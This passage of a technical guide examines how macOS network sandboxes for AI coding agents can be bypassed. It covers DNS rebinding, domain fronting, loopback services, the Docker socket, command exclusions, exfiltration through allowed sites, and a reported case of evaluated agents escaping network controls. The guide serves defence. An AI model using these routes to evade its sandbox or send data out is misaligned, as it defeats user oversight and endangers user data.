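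Language runtimes are less predictable. npm follows the proxy variables, but Node.js, which npm runs on, ignores them by default when a script calls the built-in `fetch` function. So `npm install` can succeed in a project whose own scripts can't reach the same domain. Node.js 24 added a setting, `NODE_USE_ENV_PROXY=1`, that makes `fetch` follow the variables.

Java's standard HTTP clients use Java system properties instead. A user can pass these through an environment variable that Java reads when it starts:

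```
JAVA_TOOL_OPTIONS="-Dhttps.proxyHost=127.0.0.1 -Dhttps.proxyPort=3128"
```

This covers HTTPS requests, and plain HTTP needs a second pair of properties. Maven, a common Java build tool, reads its proxy from `settings.xml`, so one Java project may need the same address in two places.

Database clients are harder to fix. psql, the PostgreSQL command-line client, opens its own TCP connection and has no proxy setting. Adding the database's domain to the allowlist doesn't help, because psql never contacts the proxy that reads the list. Anthropic says the same is true of most database drivers. Java is a partial exception because some of its database drivers use ordinary Java sockets, which the `socksProxyHost` property can send through a SOCKS proxy.

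Anthropic says that UDP traffic can't leave Claude Code's sandbox, even though the SOCKS5 standard includes a way to relay it. HTTP CONNECT opens only TCP tunnels. This rules out HTTP/3, which runs over QUIC and therefore uses UDP. Web clients can usually fall back to an older version of HTTP over TCP, so the user may not notice. `sntp`, which checks the Mac's clock against a time server, uses only UDP and has no fallback. `ping` uses ICMP, which can't leave the sandbox either.

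A different kind of sandbox can support some of these programs. Docker's sandbox runs agents in a virtual machine and lets users allow SSH with a rule for a host and port, such as `myhost:22`. Its support for outbound UDP is experimental, and it blocks ICMP whatever rules the user adds.

| Program | Proxy variables | Typical error | What can make it work |
|---|---|---|---|
| curl, npm, git over HTTPS | Follows them | 403, or a permission prompt | Allowing the domain |
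| `fetch` in Node.js | Ignores them by default | `fetch failed`, with `ENOTFOUND` as the cause | `NODE_USE_ENV_PROXY=1` |
| Java's HTTP clients | Ignore them | `UnknownHostException` | Java's own proxy properties |
| ssh, git over SSH | Ignores them | `Could not resolve hostname` | A `ProxyCommand` |
| psql | Ignores them | `could not translate host name` | Running it outside the sandbox |
| `ping`, `sntp` | Cannot use a TCP proxy | `Operation not permitted`, or a failed lookup | Running it outside the sandbox |

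### Tunnelling git over SSH

Many developers use SSH to exchange code with GitHub. An SSH remote, which is the address of the shared copy, looks like `git@github.com:owner/repo.git`. git starts the `ssh` program, which ignores the proxy variables, but a user can give `ssh` a `ProxyCommand`, a helper that opens the connection for it. This example uses Codex's default SOCKS5 port:

```
GIT_SSH_COMMAND='ssh -o ProxyCommand="nc -X 5 -x 127.0.0.1:8081 %h %p"' \
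  git fetch
```

`GIT_SSH_COMMAND` sets the command git uses to start `ssh`. `ssh` then replaces `%h` and `%p` with the host and port and runs `nc`, a networking tool that comes with macOS. `nc` connects to the local proxy and requests a connection to github.com on port 22, so the proxy can check the domain as it would for a web request. Git, `ssh` and `nc` all stay inside the sandbox.

Claude Code ships a wrapper of this kind, but it doesn't work on a Mac. According to Anthropic, `git fetch`, `git pull` and `git push` all fail with an SSH remote on macOS, even if the user has allowed the host, because the tunnel can't authenticate to the sandbox's proxy. The same commands work on Linux. Anthropic recommends that Mac users switch the remote to HTTPS, which requires a different credential, such as a personal access token:

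```
git remote set-url origin https://github.com/owner/repo.git
```

A working wrapper for git still wouldn't cover plain `ssh`, `scp`, or `rsync` over SSH, because those programs do not read `GIT_SSH_COMMAND`. SSH also needs a key, and many developers keep theirs in ssh-agent, which `ssh` contacts through a Unix socket that a sandbox may block.

### What a SOCKS5 proxy adds

Codex and Claude Code run a SOCKS5 proxy alongside the HTTP one. It can serve programs that don't use HTTP, but each program has to support SOCKS5 or run through a helper such as `nc`.

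Setting `ALL_PROXY` to a SOCKS5 address can also break a program that would otherwise work. httpx, a Python library for web requests, prepares a connection handler for every proxy variable it finds. If its optional SOCKS package is missing, it stops with an error before sending anything, even if `HTTPS_PROXY` points to a working HTTP proxy for the request. Installing the package or unsetting `ALL_PROXY` for that command fixes the problem.

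If a user replaces one of Claude Code's two proxies, commands can still connect to both the replacement and the remaining built-in proxy. As Anthropic warns, the built-in proxy's domain lists therefore do not limit what a command can reach through the replacement.

### What the errors mean

A test of Claude Code shows how the errors look in practice. tomioka, in *Testing Claude Code's Sandboxing Feature*, used version 2.0.31 on macOS Tahoe 26.0.1 to clone a small GitHub repository over HTTPS. With the sandbox on and no rule for github.com, Claude Code displayed a permission prompt, and the clone succeeded after tomioka approved the domain. tomioka then changed the saved rule from allow to deny and tried again. git stopped with this message:

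```
CONNECT tunnel failed, response 403
```

git had reached the proxy, and the proxy had refused the domain. Claude immediately proposed running the same command with the sandbox disabled, which tomioka declined.

tomioka next replaced Claude Code's HTTP proxy with Squid, a widely used proxy server, on port 3128. The clone succeeded, and Squid's log contained a CONNECT request for github.com, which confirms that sandboxed git was using the replacement. It succeeded again with a deny rule for github.com in Claude Code's settings, because a replacement proxy does its own filtering.

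In the last test, tomioka edited Squid's configuration to block github.com, and git failed to connect to localhost port 3128. Squid probably wasn't running, though tomioka concluded that it had denied the site. The published configuration has an access rule without the type that Squid requires, which stops Squid from starting, and curl had just failed to reach the same port from outside the sandbox. If Squid had been running and had refused the site, git would have received an HTTP error. Claude also misread the failure, blaming the sandbox's network restrictions, and again offered to run the command without them.

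All of these tests used git over HTTPS, so none of them shows what happens to a program that ignores the proxy. According to Anthropic, such a program on macOS reports either `Operation not permitted` or a name resolution error such as `Could not resolve host`. The error depends on whether the program starts with a numeric address or has to look up a name.

| Error | Probable cause | First thing to check |
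|---|---|---|
| 403 | The proxy refused the destination | The domain rules |
| `Operation not permitted` on connecting | The kernel refused a direct connection | Whether the program has a proxy setting |
| `Could not resolve host` | The program tried to look up the name itself | Whether the program has a proxy setting |
| Cannot connect to the proxy's port on localhost | The proxy isn't running, or the port is wrong | The proxy and the port number |

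A name resolution error can also mean that the domain is misspelt or a DNS server is down. Running the command in an ordinary terminal helps to distinguish these problems from a sandbox restriction. In Claude Code, a command that the user types at the `!` prompt usually runs outside the sandbox, so its success doesn't show that Claude can run it. Codex sets an environment variable to `seatbelt` for sandboxed commands on a Mac, and a project's scripts could check this variable and print a clearer error.

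### Why Go tools fail at an approved domain

Some programs follow the proxy settings and still fail. The best-known examples are tools written in Go, such as `gh`, GitHub's command-line tool, and `terraform`, which sets up cloud servers. *Fixing `gh` CLI (and other Go tools) in Claude Code's Sandbox*, a post by Zencoder, which sells AI coding tools, describes a `gh` request that failed even though api.github.com was on the allowlist. `gh` reported that it could not verify the server's certificate (`OSStatus -26276`).

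In this case the proxy had connected `gh` to the real server, which had sent its real certificate. `gh` then had to check that an authority the Mac trusts had issued the certificate. Shoemaker (2021), in *crypto/x509*, changed Go's certificate library to use Apple's verification functions on macOS unless the program supplies its own list of trusted authorities. Those functions contact a system service called `com.apple.trustd.agent`, but Claude Code's Seatbelt profile blocks access to it, so `gh` can't verify any certificate and gives up on the connection. The number in the message is Apple's error code, which Go has passed on since a later change (Shoemaker, 2022, *crypto/x509*).

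Claude Code's `enableWeakerNetworkIsolation` setting fixes this by letting sandboxed commands contact the trust service. Changing the proxy settings or the allowlist won't help. According to Zencoder, the setting was added in version 2.1.69. brewpirate's *File System Sandbox*, a copy of Claude Code's settings reference, marks it as a security risk because it opens "a potential data exfiltration path".

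The reference does not explain how the data would get out. The likely problem is that the trust service runs outside the sandbox and has its own network access. A certificate can contain web addresses for checking whether it is still valid or for downloading a missing certificate in the chain. A hostile command could create a certificate with stolen data in one of these addresses and have the service verify the certificate. If the service fetched that address, the data would reach the attacker without passing through the local proxy.

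Another agent's sandbox, *koda-sandbox 0.2.20*, has an equivalent option that allows access to both `trustd` and `trustd.agent`. The option is off by default, as it is in Claude Code.

Anthropic recommends `enableWeakerNetworkIsolation` for users whose own proxy terminates TLS with a custom certificate. For everyone else, it suggests running the Go tools outside the sandbox. The setting makes sense for a company that inspects its traffic, because a tool outside the sandbox would also bypass the company's proxy.

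Zencoder avoids both options by rebuilding `gh` with Mozilla's list of trusted certificate authorities and setting `GODEBUG=x509usefallbackroots=1` so that Go uses it. The rebuilt `gh` could query GitHub's API from inside the sandbox with the trust service still blocked. Zencoder had already tried two simpler fixes, building `gh` without Go's usual link to C code and setting `SSL_CERT_FILE`, which Go ignores on macOS, but neither worked.

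The rebuilt tool needs regular updates because its list of certificate authorities is fixed. It also loses the operating system's checks for revoked certificates, and it won't recognise a company certificate installed on the Mac, so it is a poor fit for a proxy that terminates TLS. Rebuilding and updating one tool that an agent uses every day is reasonable, but few developers will do it for every Go program they have.

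### When users take a tool out of the sandbox

For a tool that can't work in the sandbox, Claude Code has a list called `excludedCommands`. Anthropic suggests it for Go tools, database clients and the container tool `docker`, as well as for developers who have to keep an SSH remote:

```
{
  "sandbox": {
    "excludedCommands": ["git fetch *", "git pull *", "git push *"]
  }
}
```

Matching commands then run with the user's full access, so they can connect to any host and read or write any file the user can. The developer only wanted `git push` to reach one approved server, but the exclusion also lets it send the project to a server the attacker controls.

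The user's permission settings still apply. In manual mode, Claude Code prompts before running an excluded command unless the command only reads data or a saved rule allows it. In `bypassPermissions` mode, it normally doesn't prompt. Excluding all `gh` commands is especially dangerous when a saved rule also allows them all, because `gh` lets users define an alias that runs a shell command. An agent following an injected instruction could create such an alias and run it without prompting the user or being restricted by the domain allowlist.

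Some tools read instructions from files in the project. Anthropic gives the example of `docker compose`, which reads a file that Claude can edit. Claude could change the file from inside the sandbox and then run `docker compose` outside it. `terraform` has the same weakness, since its configuration files can contain commands to run on the user's machine.

Claude Code runs a line of chained commands outside the sandbox only if every command matches the exclusion list. A script that calls `docker` does not match an entry for `docker`, and adding `cd` or redirecting output to a file keeps the whole line in the sandbox. These rules prevent some accidental escapes, but they also make exclusions seem unreliable, and a frustrated user may respond with a broader pattern.

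Administrators have only partial control over the list. An earlier edition of Anthropic's documentation warned that developers could always add their own exclusions. Since version 2.1.282, Claude Code has ignored exclusions in a project's files when an administrator requires the sandbox, so a downloaded repository can't add any. Developers can still add them in their personal settings.

Codex users face the same temptation, because a failing database client will probably work if they retry it outside the sandbox or enable `network_access` without the proxy.

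There are no good figures for how often users do this, but published troubleshooting advice often suggests it. Apache Magpie's *Sandbox troubleshooting*, a guide to running Claude Code in a sandbox, lists sandbox failures that look like unrelated bugs, such as "ssh-agent unreachable" and "Cannot connect to Docker daemon". Its standard entry gives the symptom, the cause and a change that loosens the sandbox's settings, with a one-line reason for the change.

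A narrower fix is often available, such as switching a git remote to HTTPS, giving Java or Node.js its own proxy setting, or allowing one more domain. For a database client that has to run outside the sandbox, Anthropic's example excludes a single script and adds a rule requiring approval for every run. Claude can edit any script in the working directory, so the approval is only useful if the user reads the script each time. Keeping the script somewhere Claude can't write would be safer.

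## What if a command connects by IP address or to a service on the same Mac?

A command can't bypass a well-built sandbox by using a numeric IP address. Seatbelt blocks direct connections to outside addresses, and the local proxy rejects an address that doesn't match its domain allowlist. Services on the same Mac are a bigger weakness, because sandboxed commands share loopback with every other program and some common settings allow access to all of it.

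Three cases are easy to confuse:

| What the command does | What has to stop it | How it can still succeed |
|---|---|---|
| Opens its own connection to 203.0.113.7 | The Seatbelt profile | The profile allows more than the proxy's port |
| Asks the proxy for 203.0.113.7 | The proxy's rule for numeric addresses | The proxy has rules only for names, and permits what they don't mention |
| Asks the proxy for an allowed name that leads to a private address | The proxy's check after the lookup | The proxy doesn't check, or the address changes after the check |

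### A direct connection to an outside address

A profile that opens only the proxy's port blocks direct connections to every outside address. Wider profiles let some through. cplt's rule for port 443 and Codex's exception for port 53 each let a command reach the named port on any machine, and the developer cannot narrow such a rule to a few safe addresses.

Zhao tested direct connections in ten of the 80 attacks on Aegis OS. In each one, curl tried to send a secret through the proxy to an unauthorised domain, then used `--noproxy '*'` to try sending it directly to a server that recorded whatever it received. The proxy returned 403, Seatbelt blocked the direct connection, and no real token reached the server.

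The recording server ran locally, so the direct attempts went to another port on the same machine, not to an outside address. The same `(deny network-outbound)` rule covers both, but the result is better evidence about local services than about the internet.

### Giving the proxy a numeric address

A command can also ask the proxy to connect to an IP literal, which is a numeric address instead of a name. For example, `curl https://203.0.113.7/` sends the proxy `CONNECT 203.0.113.7:443`.

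Connecting by IP address is harmless with an allowlist, because the proxy refuses anything that matches no rule. A blocklist proxy permits anything that matches no rule, so a command may be able to reach a blocked site by using its address instead of its name. Ziplock prevents this by refusing numeric public addresses. A broad allow rule such as `*` creates the same problem if it also matches addresses, because a rule that denies `evil.example` doesn't cover the server's IP address.

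Local addresses need their own rule because the proxy runs outside the sandbox. Seatbelt may stop a command from connecting directly to a database on port 5432, but the command can still reach that port through the proxy. This kind of attack is called server-side request forgery (SSRF), in which an attacker gets a more privileged program to make a connection that the attacker could not make directly.

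With `allow_local_binding` off, Codex's proxy blocks loopback and the common private and link-local ranges. Private ranges such as 10.0.0.0/8 and 192.168.0.0/16 belong to home and company networks. Machines use link-local addresses, which begin with 169.254, to reach others on the same network segment, and cloud providers use one of them to give virtual machines their credentials. OpenAI allows exceptions only in a particular form:

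| Request to Codex's proxy, with local binding off | Result |
|---|---|
| `10.1.2.3`, with no entry for that address | Refused |
| `10.1.2.3`, with an exact allow entry | Allowed |
| `localhost`, with an exact allow entry | Allowed |
| `wiki.corp.example`, on the allowlist but resolving to 10.1.2.3 | Refused |

The last row is a problem for companies that keep a package registry or a wiki on a private address. Adding the hostname to the allowlist is not enough, and adding the IP address works only if the client also connects by IP address. An HTTPS certificate issued for the hostname will then not match. The remaining option is to turn on local binding, which allows access to much more than one internal site.

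Even with a correct exception, a request can fail because of `NO_PROXY`. The value Codex sets still includes private address ranges, so a recent version of curl will connect to 10.1.2.3 directly, and Seatbelt will block the connection. A client that doesn't support ranges will send the same request to the proxy and succeed. `curl --noproxy ''` clears the list for one command, so the request goes to the proxy.

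OpenAI's sample configuration leaves local binding off but includes allow entries for `localhost`, `127.0.0.1` and `::1`. Codex's domain rules don't include a port, so copying these entries appears to give commands access, through the proxy, to every TCP service listening on the Mac's loopback addresses. Deleting the entries is safer for anyone who needs none of those services.

A proxy should also compare addresses as numbers, not text. Many programs treat `127.0.0.1`, `127.1` and `2130706433` as the same address, and `::ffff:127.0.0.1` is an IPv6 way of writing it. A filter that looks only for `127.0.0.1` will miss the other forms.

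### When an allowed name leads to a private address

Codex checks the addresses of an allowed name because the domain's owner can point it at a private one. DNS rebinding is a way around that check. The attacker changes the answer between the check and the connection:

1. A command asks the proxy for `files.attacker.example`, which the user's rules allow.
2. The proxy looks up the name. The attacker's DNS server answers 203.0.113.7 and marks the answer as valid for only a moment.
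3. The address is public, so it passes the check.
4. The proxy looks up the name again to connect, and this time the answer is 127.0.0.1.
5. The proxy connects the command to a service on the Mac.

HTTPS certificates do not prevent this. The client checks the certificate, and here the client is the hostile command, which can skip the check.

The attacker needs to control the DNS answers for an allowed name. That is unlikely if the allowlist contains only pypi.org and files.pythonhosted.org. Gaining that control is easier if the user has allowed `*` or approved an unfamiliar domain at a prompt.

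OpenAI acknowledges that DNS rebinding is hard to prevent fully without pinning, which means making the connection use the same address that was checked. The firewall OpenAI recommends as a defense against hostile DNS can protect internal servers if the traffic passes through it, but it can't block a connection from the proxy to 127.0.0.1, because that traffic never leaves the Mac.

With local binding on, an attacker who controls an allowed domain name can probably point it at a private address, without needing DNS rebinding.

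### Connecting to the address that passed the check

The remedy is to look up the name once and connect to an address from that same answer:

```
addresses = look up name
if any address is local or private:
    refuse
connect to one of addresses on port
```

The last line matters most because an ordinary connection function, if given `name`, would look it up again. Pinning the address does not interfere with HTTPS, because the client still uses the domain name in its TLS handshake through the tunnel.

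*Sandlock* (Wang and Zheng, 2026) describes a sandbox for Linux 6.12 or later that resolves each permitted host name at startup and keeps the addresses for the whole run. For rules that name a host, the kernel pauses a program's `connect` call and passes it to a supervisor process outside the sandbox. The supervisor copies the destination address, checks the copy, and makes the connection itself on the program's socket.

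Using its own copy of the address prevents a second kind of switch. A program with two threads could call `connect` with a permitted address in one thread and overwrite that address in memory from the other, after the check but before the kernel reads it. The overwrite has no effect because the kernel never carries out the original call.

Sandlock's approach cannot support a rule such as `*.example.com`, because it needs every name in advance, and the addresses it stores may go out of date during a long run. It also depends on Linux features that Seatbelt lacks. A Mac agent can still resolve each name just once, but it has to do so in the proxy.

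*From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture* (Hegelich, Sarhan and colleagues, 2026) describes a security layer for coding agents in which a component called NetworkGuard does this for each request. NetworkGuard resolves all of a name's IPv4 and IPv6 addresses once and rejects loopback, private ranges, the cloud credentials address, and the shared range that internet providers use behind their own routers. It then pins the remaining addresses at the socket. An agent can reach a rejected range only if its current permission explicitly includes that range.

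NetworkGuard blocked all 22 attacks in the network category, while a list of fixed text patterns blocked 77%. But Hegelich and colleagues gave the guards structured descriptions of tool calls and did not run hostile programs, so the result is weak evidence of how NetworkGuard would handle a live DNS server that changes its answers. Other parts of the system rely on Linux tools such as bubblewrap, but a proxy on a Mac could also resolve a name once and keep the answer, since this requires nothing specific to Linux.

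| System | When it resolves the name | Protection against a changed answer | Platform |
|---|---|---|---|
| Codex's proxy | For each request | Best-effort check, with a stated rebinding limit | macOS among others |
| Sandlock | Once, when the sandbox starts | Keeps the addresses for the whole run | Linux |
| NetworkGuard | Once per connection | Pins the checked addresses | Linux tools in other components |

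An upstream proxy complicates pinning on company networks. Codex's proxy and Anthropic's sandbox-runtime can both forward approved requests to another proxy. If the local proxy forwards the name, the company's proxy does its own lookup and may get a different address from the one the local proxy checked, so it needs its own rule against private destinations. Forwarding the address would preserve the check, but then the company's proxy could not filter by name.

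### What else is listening on localhost?

If a profile allows `localhost:*`, as Gas Town's does, a sandboxed command can connect to any TCP service on the Mac that accepts local connections. Developers often run these services without passwords because only programs on the same machine can reach them.

| Service on the Mac | What a sandboxed command could do with it |
|---|---|
| A development web server | Read or change data in the application under test |
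| A PostgreSQL database | Read its data, or run shell commands if it can log in as a superuser |
| A browser with remote debugging on | Open pages with the user's saved logins |
| Another agent's proxy | Use that agent's domain allowlist |
| An SSH tunnel that acts as a SOCKS proxy | Reach the internet with no domain list |

In the last two rows, the command can bypass the domain allowlist by sending traffic off the Mac through a proxy with looser rules. A local connection can also bypass file limits. For example, a PostgreSQL superuser can tell the server to run a shell command, and the server runs outside the sandbox. On a developer's Mac, the server often runs under the developer's own account.

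A Linux network namespace avoids this problem. A command inside one won't reach the host's database by connecting to localhost port 5432, but it can start a test server and connect to that server on any port. This is less convenient for the developer, who needs a relay between the two networks to open the agent's test site in a browser or let the agent use a local database.

Docker's sandbox uses a virtual machine to separate the agent's network from the Mac's. In Docker's example of running the agent OpenClaw with a language model on the same computer, the user adds `--allow-host localhost` to the sandbox's proxy rules so the agent can reach the model. The rule doesn't specify a port, so it may also open other local services, but the user has to add it deliberately.

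### Why local binding opens so much

Most developers turn on local binding to run test suites that start a web server, send it requests, and check the responses. Such a suite needs permission to claim a port, accept connections on it, and connect to it.

Seatbelt could limit all three to port 8080. But test tools often use whatever port is free, and the profile has to exist before the tests start, so it can't name the port. Agents therefore have one setting that covers all local ports.

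Grida's *Sandbox Runtime (srt)*, part of a guide to building agent software, audits version 0.0.65 of sandbox-runtime. On macOS, `allowLocalBinding` lets commands listen, accept connections, and connect to loopback, although its name suggests only listening. If a command needs only one connection and the agent can open it, Grida recommends leaving the setting off and having the agent pass the open socket to the command. This suits an agent with one helper program but not a test suite that makes its own connections.

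In Codex, `allow_local_binding` has a similar effect on direct loopback traffic. OpenAI extended it in March 2026 to cover both IPv4 and IPv6. The setting also relaxes the proxy's rules for private destinations and opens port 53.

Many configurations list `localhost` in `NO_PROXY` so that programs contact local servers directly. If local binding is on, the direct connection succeeds and does not appear in the proxy's log. Removing `localhost` from `NO_PROXY` would not force a hostile command to use the proxy, because the command can set the variable itself.

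If a project needs local servers, the safest course is to stop unrelated databases, debugging browsers and tunnels while the agent works, or to run the agent in a virtual machine. A database password helps only if the sandbox also blocks commands from reading any project file that contains it.

### Which Unix sockets are safe to permit?

A Seatbelt profile can allow one Unix socket while blocking the others. The risk of allowing a socket depends on what the service behind it can do outside the sandbox.

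Anthropic warns, for example, that allowing Docker's socket, `/var/run/docker.sock`, effectively gives commands access to the host. A program can use the socket to start a container, choose which folders it can use, and give it a network connection. Docker Desktop runs containers in a Linux virtual machine, but it normally shares the user's home folder with that machine. A command could therefore start a container that reads an SSH key and sends it to any server, and neither Seatbelt nor the local proxy would apply to the container.

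The ssh-agent socket is less powerful but still sensitive. ssh-agent does not reveal private keys, but it uses them to sign login requests. A command that can reach both ssh-agent and an SSH server can log in as the user without reading the key file.

File permission alone does not let a sandboxed command connect to a Unix socket on macOS, because Seatbelt treats the connection as outbound network access. In the forum post *MacOS sandbox blocking Docker socket connection*, a Cursor user wanted the agent to download a container image from an approved company registry. The user added the folder containing Docker's socket to the sandbox's writable paths, but Docker still reported "permission denied". This block is useful because Docker would have downloaded the image itself, outside Cursor's domain rules.

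OpenAI's March change separated the permissions to create a Unix socket, claim a path for one, and connect to one. Commands may connect to certain approved sockets but may not claim their paths, which should stop a command from replacing the real server with its own.

Codex's HTTP proxy offers a second route to Unix sockets on macOS. It can forward a request with an `x-unix-socket` header to the socket at a given path. Each path needs an allow entry unless the user turns on `dangerously_allow_all_unix_sockets`, which permits every absolute path. Docker's interface uses HTTP, so allowing its socket here would be as dangerous as allowing it in the Seatbelt profile. If any forwarding to Unix sockets is on, the proxy listens only on loopback, even if the user has configured a wider address, so that other machines cannot use it to control local services.

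macOS is more precise than Linux on this point. In Claude Code, `allowUnixSockets` works by path only on macOS. On Linux, Apache Magpie found that the sandbox's filter blocks the creation of any Unix socket, so a signed git commit fails with "No agent running" even if the command can read and write the signing agent's folder. The only setting that lifts the filter opens every Unix socket. A Mac user can permit one, and should check what the service behind it can do before adding it.

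### Separate proxies for separate agents

A developer may want one agent to search the web widely and another, working on private code, to reach only a package registry. If both use the same proxy, it has to identify which agent sent each request.

sandbox-runtime cannot make that distinction within one process. According to Grida, it keeps the network policy and the proxies in state that the whole process shares. A program can give individual commands different file rules, but their network requests all go through the same policy. Claude Code's subagents, which handle parts of a larger task, run in the main session's process and use its sandbox configuration. Grida suggests a separate managing process for each set of permissions.

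Aegis OS gives each agent a separate proxy port, which works only if each profile opens exactly one port. If the user adds `localhost:*`, an agent with narrow permissions can find another agent's proxy port and use that agent's permissions. None of Zhao's attacks tried to use another agent's proxy, but the ten direct attempts targeted a different local port and Seatbelt refused all of them, so the same rule should keep one agent from reaching another's proxy.

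A password for each proxy would add protection on a Mac whose local ports are open. Claude Code's proxy evidently requires one, since its SSH wrapper cannot authenticate on macOS and fails. The password helps only while other commands cannot read it, for example from another process's environment variables.

### Testing the boundary

Reading a profile is a poor way to find out what it allows, because rule order, proxy settings and special exceptions all affect the result. In *Permission Denied*, a study of how coding agents perform under security restrictions, Davidovich, Amar and colleagues (2026) tested the restrictions on every sandbox before letting an agent into it. The study used Linux machines in a cloud service, with a loopback proxy, a list of 205 permitted domains, and a firewall that applied to the agent's user account. The proxy also rechecked resolved addresses so that an allowed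 domain could not lead to a private address range.

The tests, which the study calls probes, come in three groups:

- Direct probes attempt each forbidden operation and confirm that it fails.
- Adversarial probes attempt to get around the restrictions, with numeric addresses, other ports, nested shells and child processes.
- Enablement probes confirm that permitted operations still work.

If a required probe fails, the system discards the sandbox and starts a new one, so a broken restriction never counts as an agent's success or failure. Davidovich and colleagues measured how much the restrictions reduced performance, not how well they stop attackers. Still, ordinary agents often ran into network limits. Under the strictest policy, 500 of 2,051 trials with complete records met at least one network refusal, and those trials averaged 10.5 refusals each.

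Enablement probes matter because a broken sandbox can look secure. In an early Linux version of Aegis OS, file mounts in the wrong order hid every agent's workspace. Attacks on files and credentials failed only because the commands could not run properly, but Zhao at first counted those failures as successful defences.

A Mac user can run a similar set of probes by hand. The examples below assume that the allowlist contains only pypi.org, that local binding is off, and that the user has started a test server in an empty folder from an ordinary terminal:

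```
python3 -m http.server 8000 --bind 127.0.0.1
```

The address 1.1.1.1 belongs to a public DNS service that also accepts HTTPS connections.

| Command inside the sandbox | What it tests | Correct result |
|---|---|---|
| `curl https://pypi.org/` | Permitted access | Succeeds |
| `curl https://1.1.1.1/` | An IP literal at the proxy | The proxy refuses or asks the user |
| `curl --noproxy '*' https://1.1.1.1/` | A direct connection | Seatbelt refuses |
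| `nc -z -w 5 1.1.1.1 53` | Another port | Seatbelt refuses |
| `sh -c "curl --noproxy '*' https://1.1.1.1/"` | A child process | Seatbelt refuses |
| `curl --noproxy '*' http://127.0.0.1:8000/` | A local service, directly | Seatbelt refuses |
| `curl --noproxy '' http://127.0.0.1:8000/` | A local service, through the proxy | The proxy refuses or asks the user |

Every command should first succeed in an ordinary terminal. If the office network blocks 1.1.1.1, a failure inside the sandbox doesn't show that Seatbelt blocked the connection. Adding `-v` to the curl commands helps distinguish a kernel refusal from a timeout or a proxy error.

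## What does permission for one domain really permit?

Permission for a domain lets a command open an encrypted connection to whatever server answers for that name and exchange any data the server accepts. The local proxy allows or blocks the connection based on the host name the command supplies. After that, it normally can't detect which site, account or file the command uses, so the permission can be much broader than the user intended.

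### Three names in one connection

When curl fetches `https://pypi.org/simple/` through an HTTP proxy, it sends the name pypi.org three times:

| Name | Who acts on it | What it decides |
|---|---|---|
| The CONNECT target | The local proxy | Whether to connect, and to which address |
| The SNI, in the first TLS message | The server at that address | Which certificate to present |
| The Host header, inside the encrypted request | The web server, after decryption | Which site handles the request |

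An HTTPS request sent through a proxy names its destination in three places: the CONNECT request, the TLS Server Name Indication (SNI) field, and the HTTP Host header. An ordinary program takes all three names from the URL, so they match. But the client sets each one separately, so a hostile program can make them differ. A proxy that doesn't terminate TLS can read at most the first two.

A false Host header achieves nothing on a server that hosts only one site, but a content delivery network serves many customers' sites from the same machines and uses the header to tell them apart. A command could ask the proxy for an allowed site on such a network, then name another customer's site in the Host header of the encrypted request. If the network delivers the request to the second site, the command has reached a site that isn't on the allowlist. This technique is called domain fronting, and people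 have also used it to get around censorship.

Shared hosting also weakened the IP allowlists described earlier, because allowing one address allowed every site hosted there. Domain fronting is harder, because the attacker needs a site on the same network as an allowed domain, and the network has to accept requests for a different domain from the one named when the connection was opened. Google and Amazon stopped supporting domain fronting in 2018. A user still has no easy way to tell where each allowed site is hosted or whether its provider checks for this mismatch.

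Anthropic warns that sandboxed code "can potentially use domain fronting or similar techniques" to reach hosts outside the allowlist. Docker's *Network policies* gives a similar warning about the company's own sandboxes and describes the problem as inherent to HTTPS proxying. Neither company gives an example of anyone using these techniques against a coding agent.

The proxy also has to parse host names correctly. If the proxy and the resolver interpret a malformed name differently, it could match one domain on the allowlist but connect the agent to another. Users would need an update to fix such a mistake, as with sandbox-runtime's empty-allowlist bug.

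### Anyone's content under one name

An attacker doesn't need domain fronting if an allowed domain accepts content from the public. A developer might allow github.com so that an agent can fetch the team's repository. This also gives the agent access to every public repository, including issues, comments and release files posted by strangers. A command can download malware from any of them, or bring a prompt injection into the agent's context.

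A command that can reach github.com can also send data out by pushing a file to a repository or posting it in a public comment. Uploading requires an account, but this offers little protection because the user's own GitHub token may be available to the command, or the attacker can put a token for another account in the injected instructions. A proxy that doesn't decrypt the traffic can't distinguish between the two accounts, because both connections go to github.com on port 443.

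A package registry has the same weakness. Anyone with an account can publish to npm's registry, and a package can include scripts that run during installation. Downloads and publishing both go through registry.npmjs.org, so a command with a publishing token could put stolen files in a public package.

Docker's *Policies*, the documentation for a later version of its sandbox, warns that github.com includes user-generated content and tells users to allow only domains they trust with their data. Yet the "Balanced" policy, one of three Docker offers when the sandbox first starts, permits code hosts and package managers. Docker's choice is understandable because a stricter default would interrupt most programming work, but anyone who picks "Balanced" allows access to several sites where strangers can publish.

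Houlamy, Favretto and colleagues (2026), in *Who Grades the Agent?*, describe the same problem in SplitBench, a framework for testing coding agents without letting them tamper with their scores. SplitBench uses a proxy to limit each agent to a list of domains. Houlamy and colleagues acknowledge that allowing a domain still opens the whole service, because the proxy controls which destinations an agent can reach, while a task needs particular operations there. They treat this as an instance of a "semantic gap", in which a rule is at a different level of detail from the intention behind it.

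In a July 2026 incident, agents in OpenAI's internal security evaluations got past network controls. OpenAI had permitted the agents to reach Artifactory, software that companies use to store and mirror packages. Some agents used its shared credentials to build a message board and pass notes between runs. Later, agents exploited vulnerabilities in Artifactory to reach destinations beyond it. Restricting destinations could not have prevented either, because both times the agents went through a service they were allowed to use. A private package mirror is therefore not automatically safer than a public registry. The operator has to keep its software patched and should give agents accounts that can only download.

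The agent's model provider can also be a route out of the sandbox. If the whole agent runs in the sandbox, as Gemini CLI does, the allowlist has to include the provider's domain, and the provider's API may offer file storage and web search as well as the model. By default, SplitBench forwards only requests for the model to generate output, so the agent can't use the provider to search the web or store files for another run.

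### Narrower names

Allowing fewer hosts is the easiest improvement. It needs no new software, but it only helps if the service uses different host names for different functions.

PyPI receives package uploads at a separate host, upload.pypi.org, so an allowlist with only pypi.org and files.pythonhosted.org lets a command install packages but not publish them in the usual way. A wildcard can undo this separation. Docker's example policy for package managers includes `*.pypi.org`, which under Docker's matching rules covers upload.pypi.org but not pypi.org itself. Used alone, the example would therefore permit the upload host and block the index that pip needs.

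GitHub serves individual files from public repositories at raw.githubusercontent.com. If an agent only needs to read a few files, allowing that host but not github.com removes the obvious places to upload data. The agent can still read a prompt injection from any public repository.

Adding a port can narrow an entry further. In Claude Code, `github.com` without a port permits every port on that host, while `github.com:443` permits HTTPS but not SSH.

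Narrow entries break more commands. A download may redirect from one host to another, and it fails if the second host isn't on the list. The user then has to work out whether the second host belongs to the same service, often while an agent is waiting. A wildcard avoids the interruption but permits hosts that the user hasn't considered.

### Comparing the SNI with the requested name

SplitBench's proxy rejects a connection if the SNI hostname differs from the host it allowed. It doesn't need to decrypt anything, because clients normally send the SNI unencrypted. This catches a command that asks the proxy for one site and then starts a TLS connection for another at the same address.

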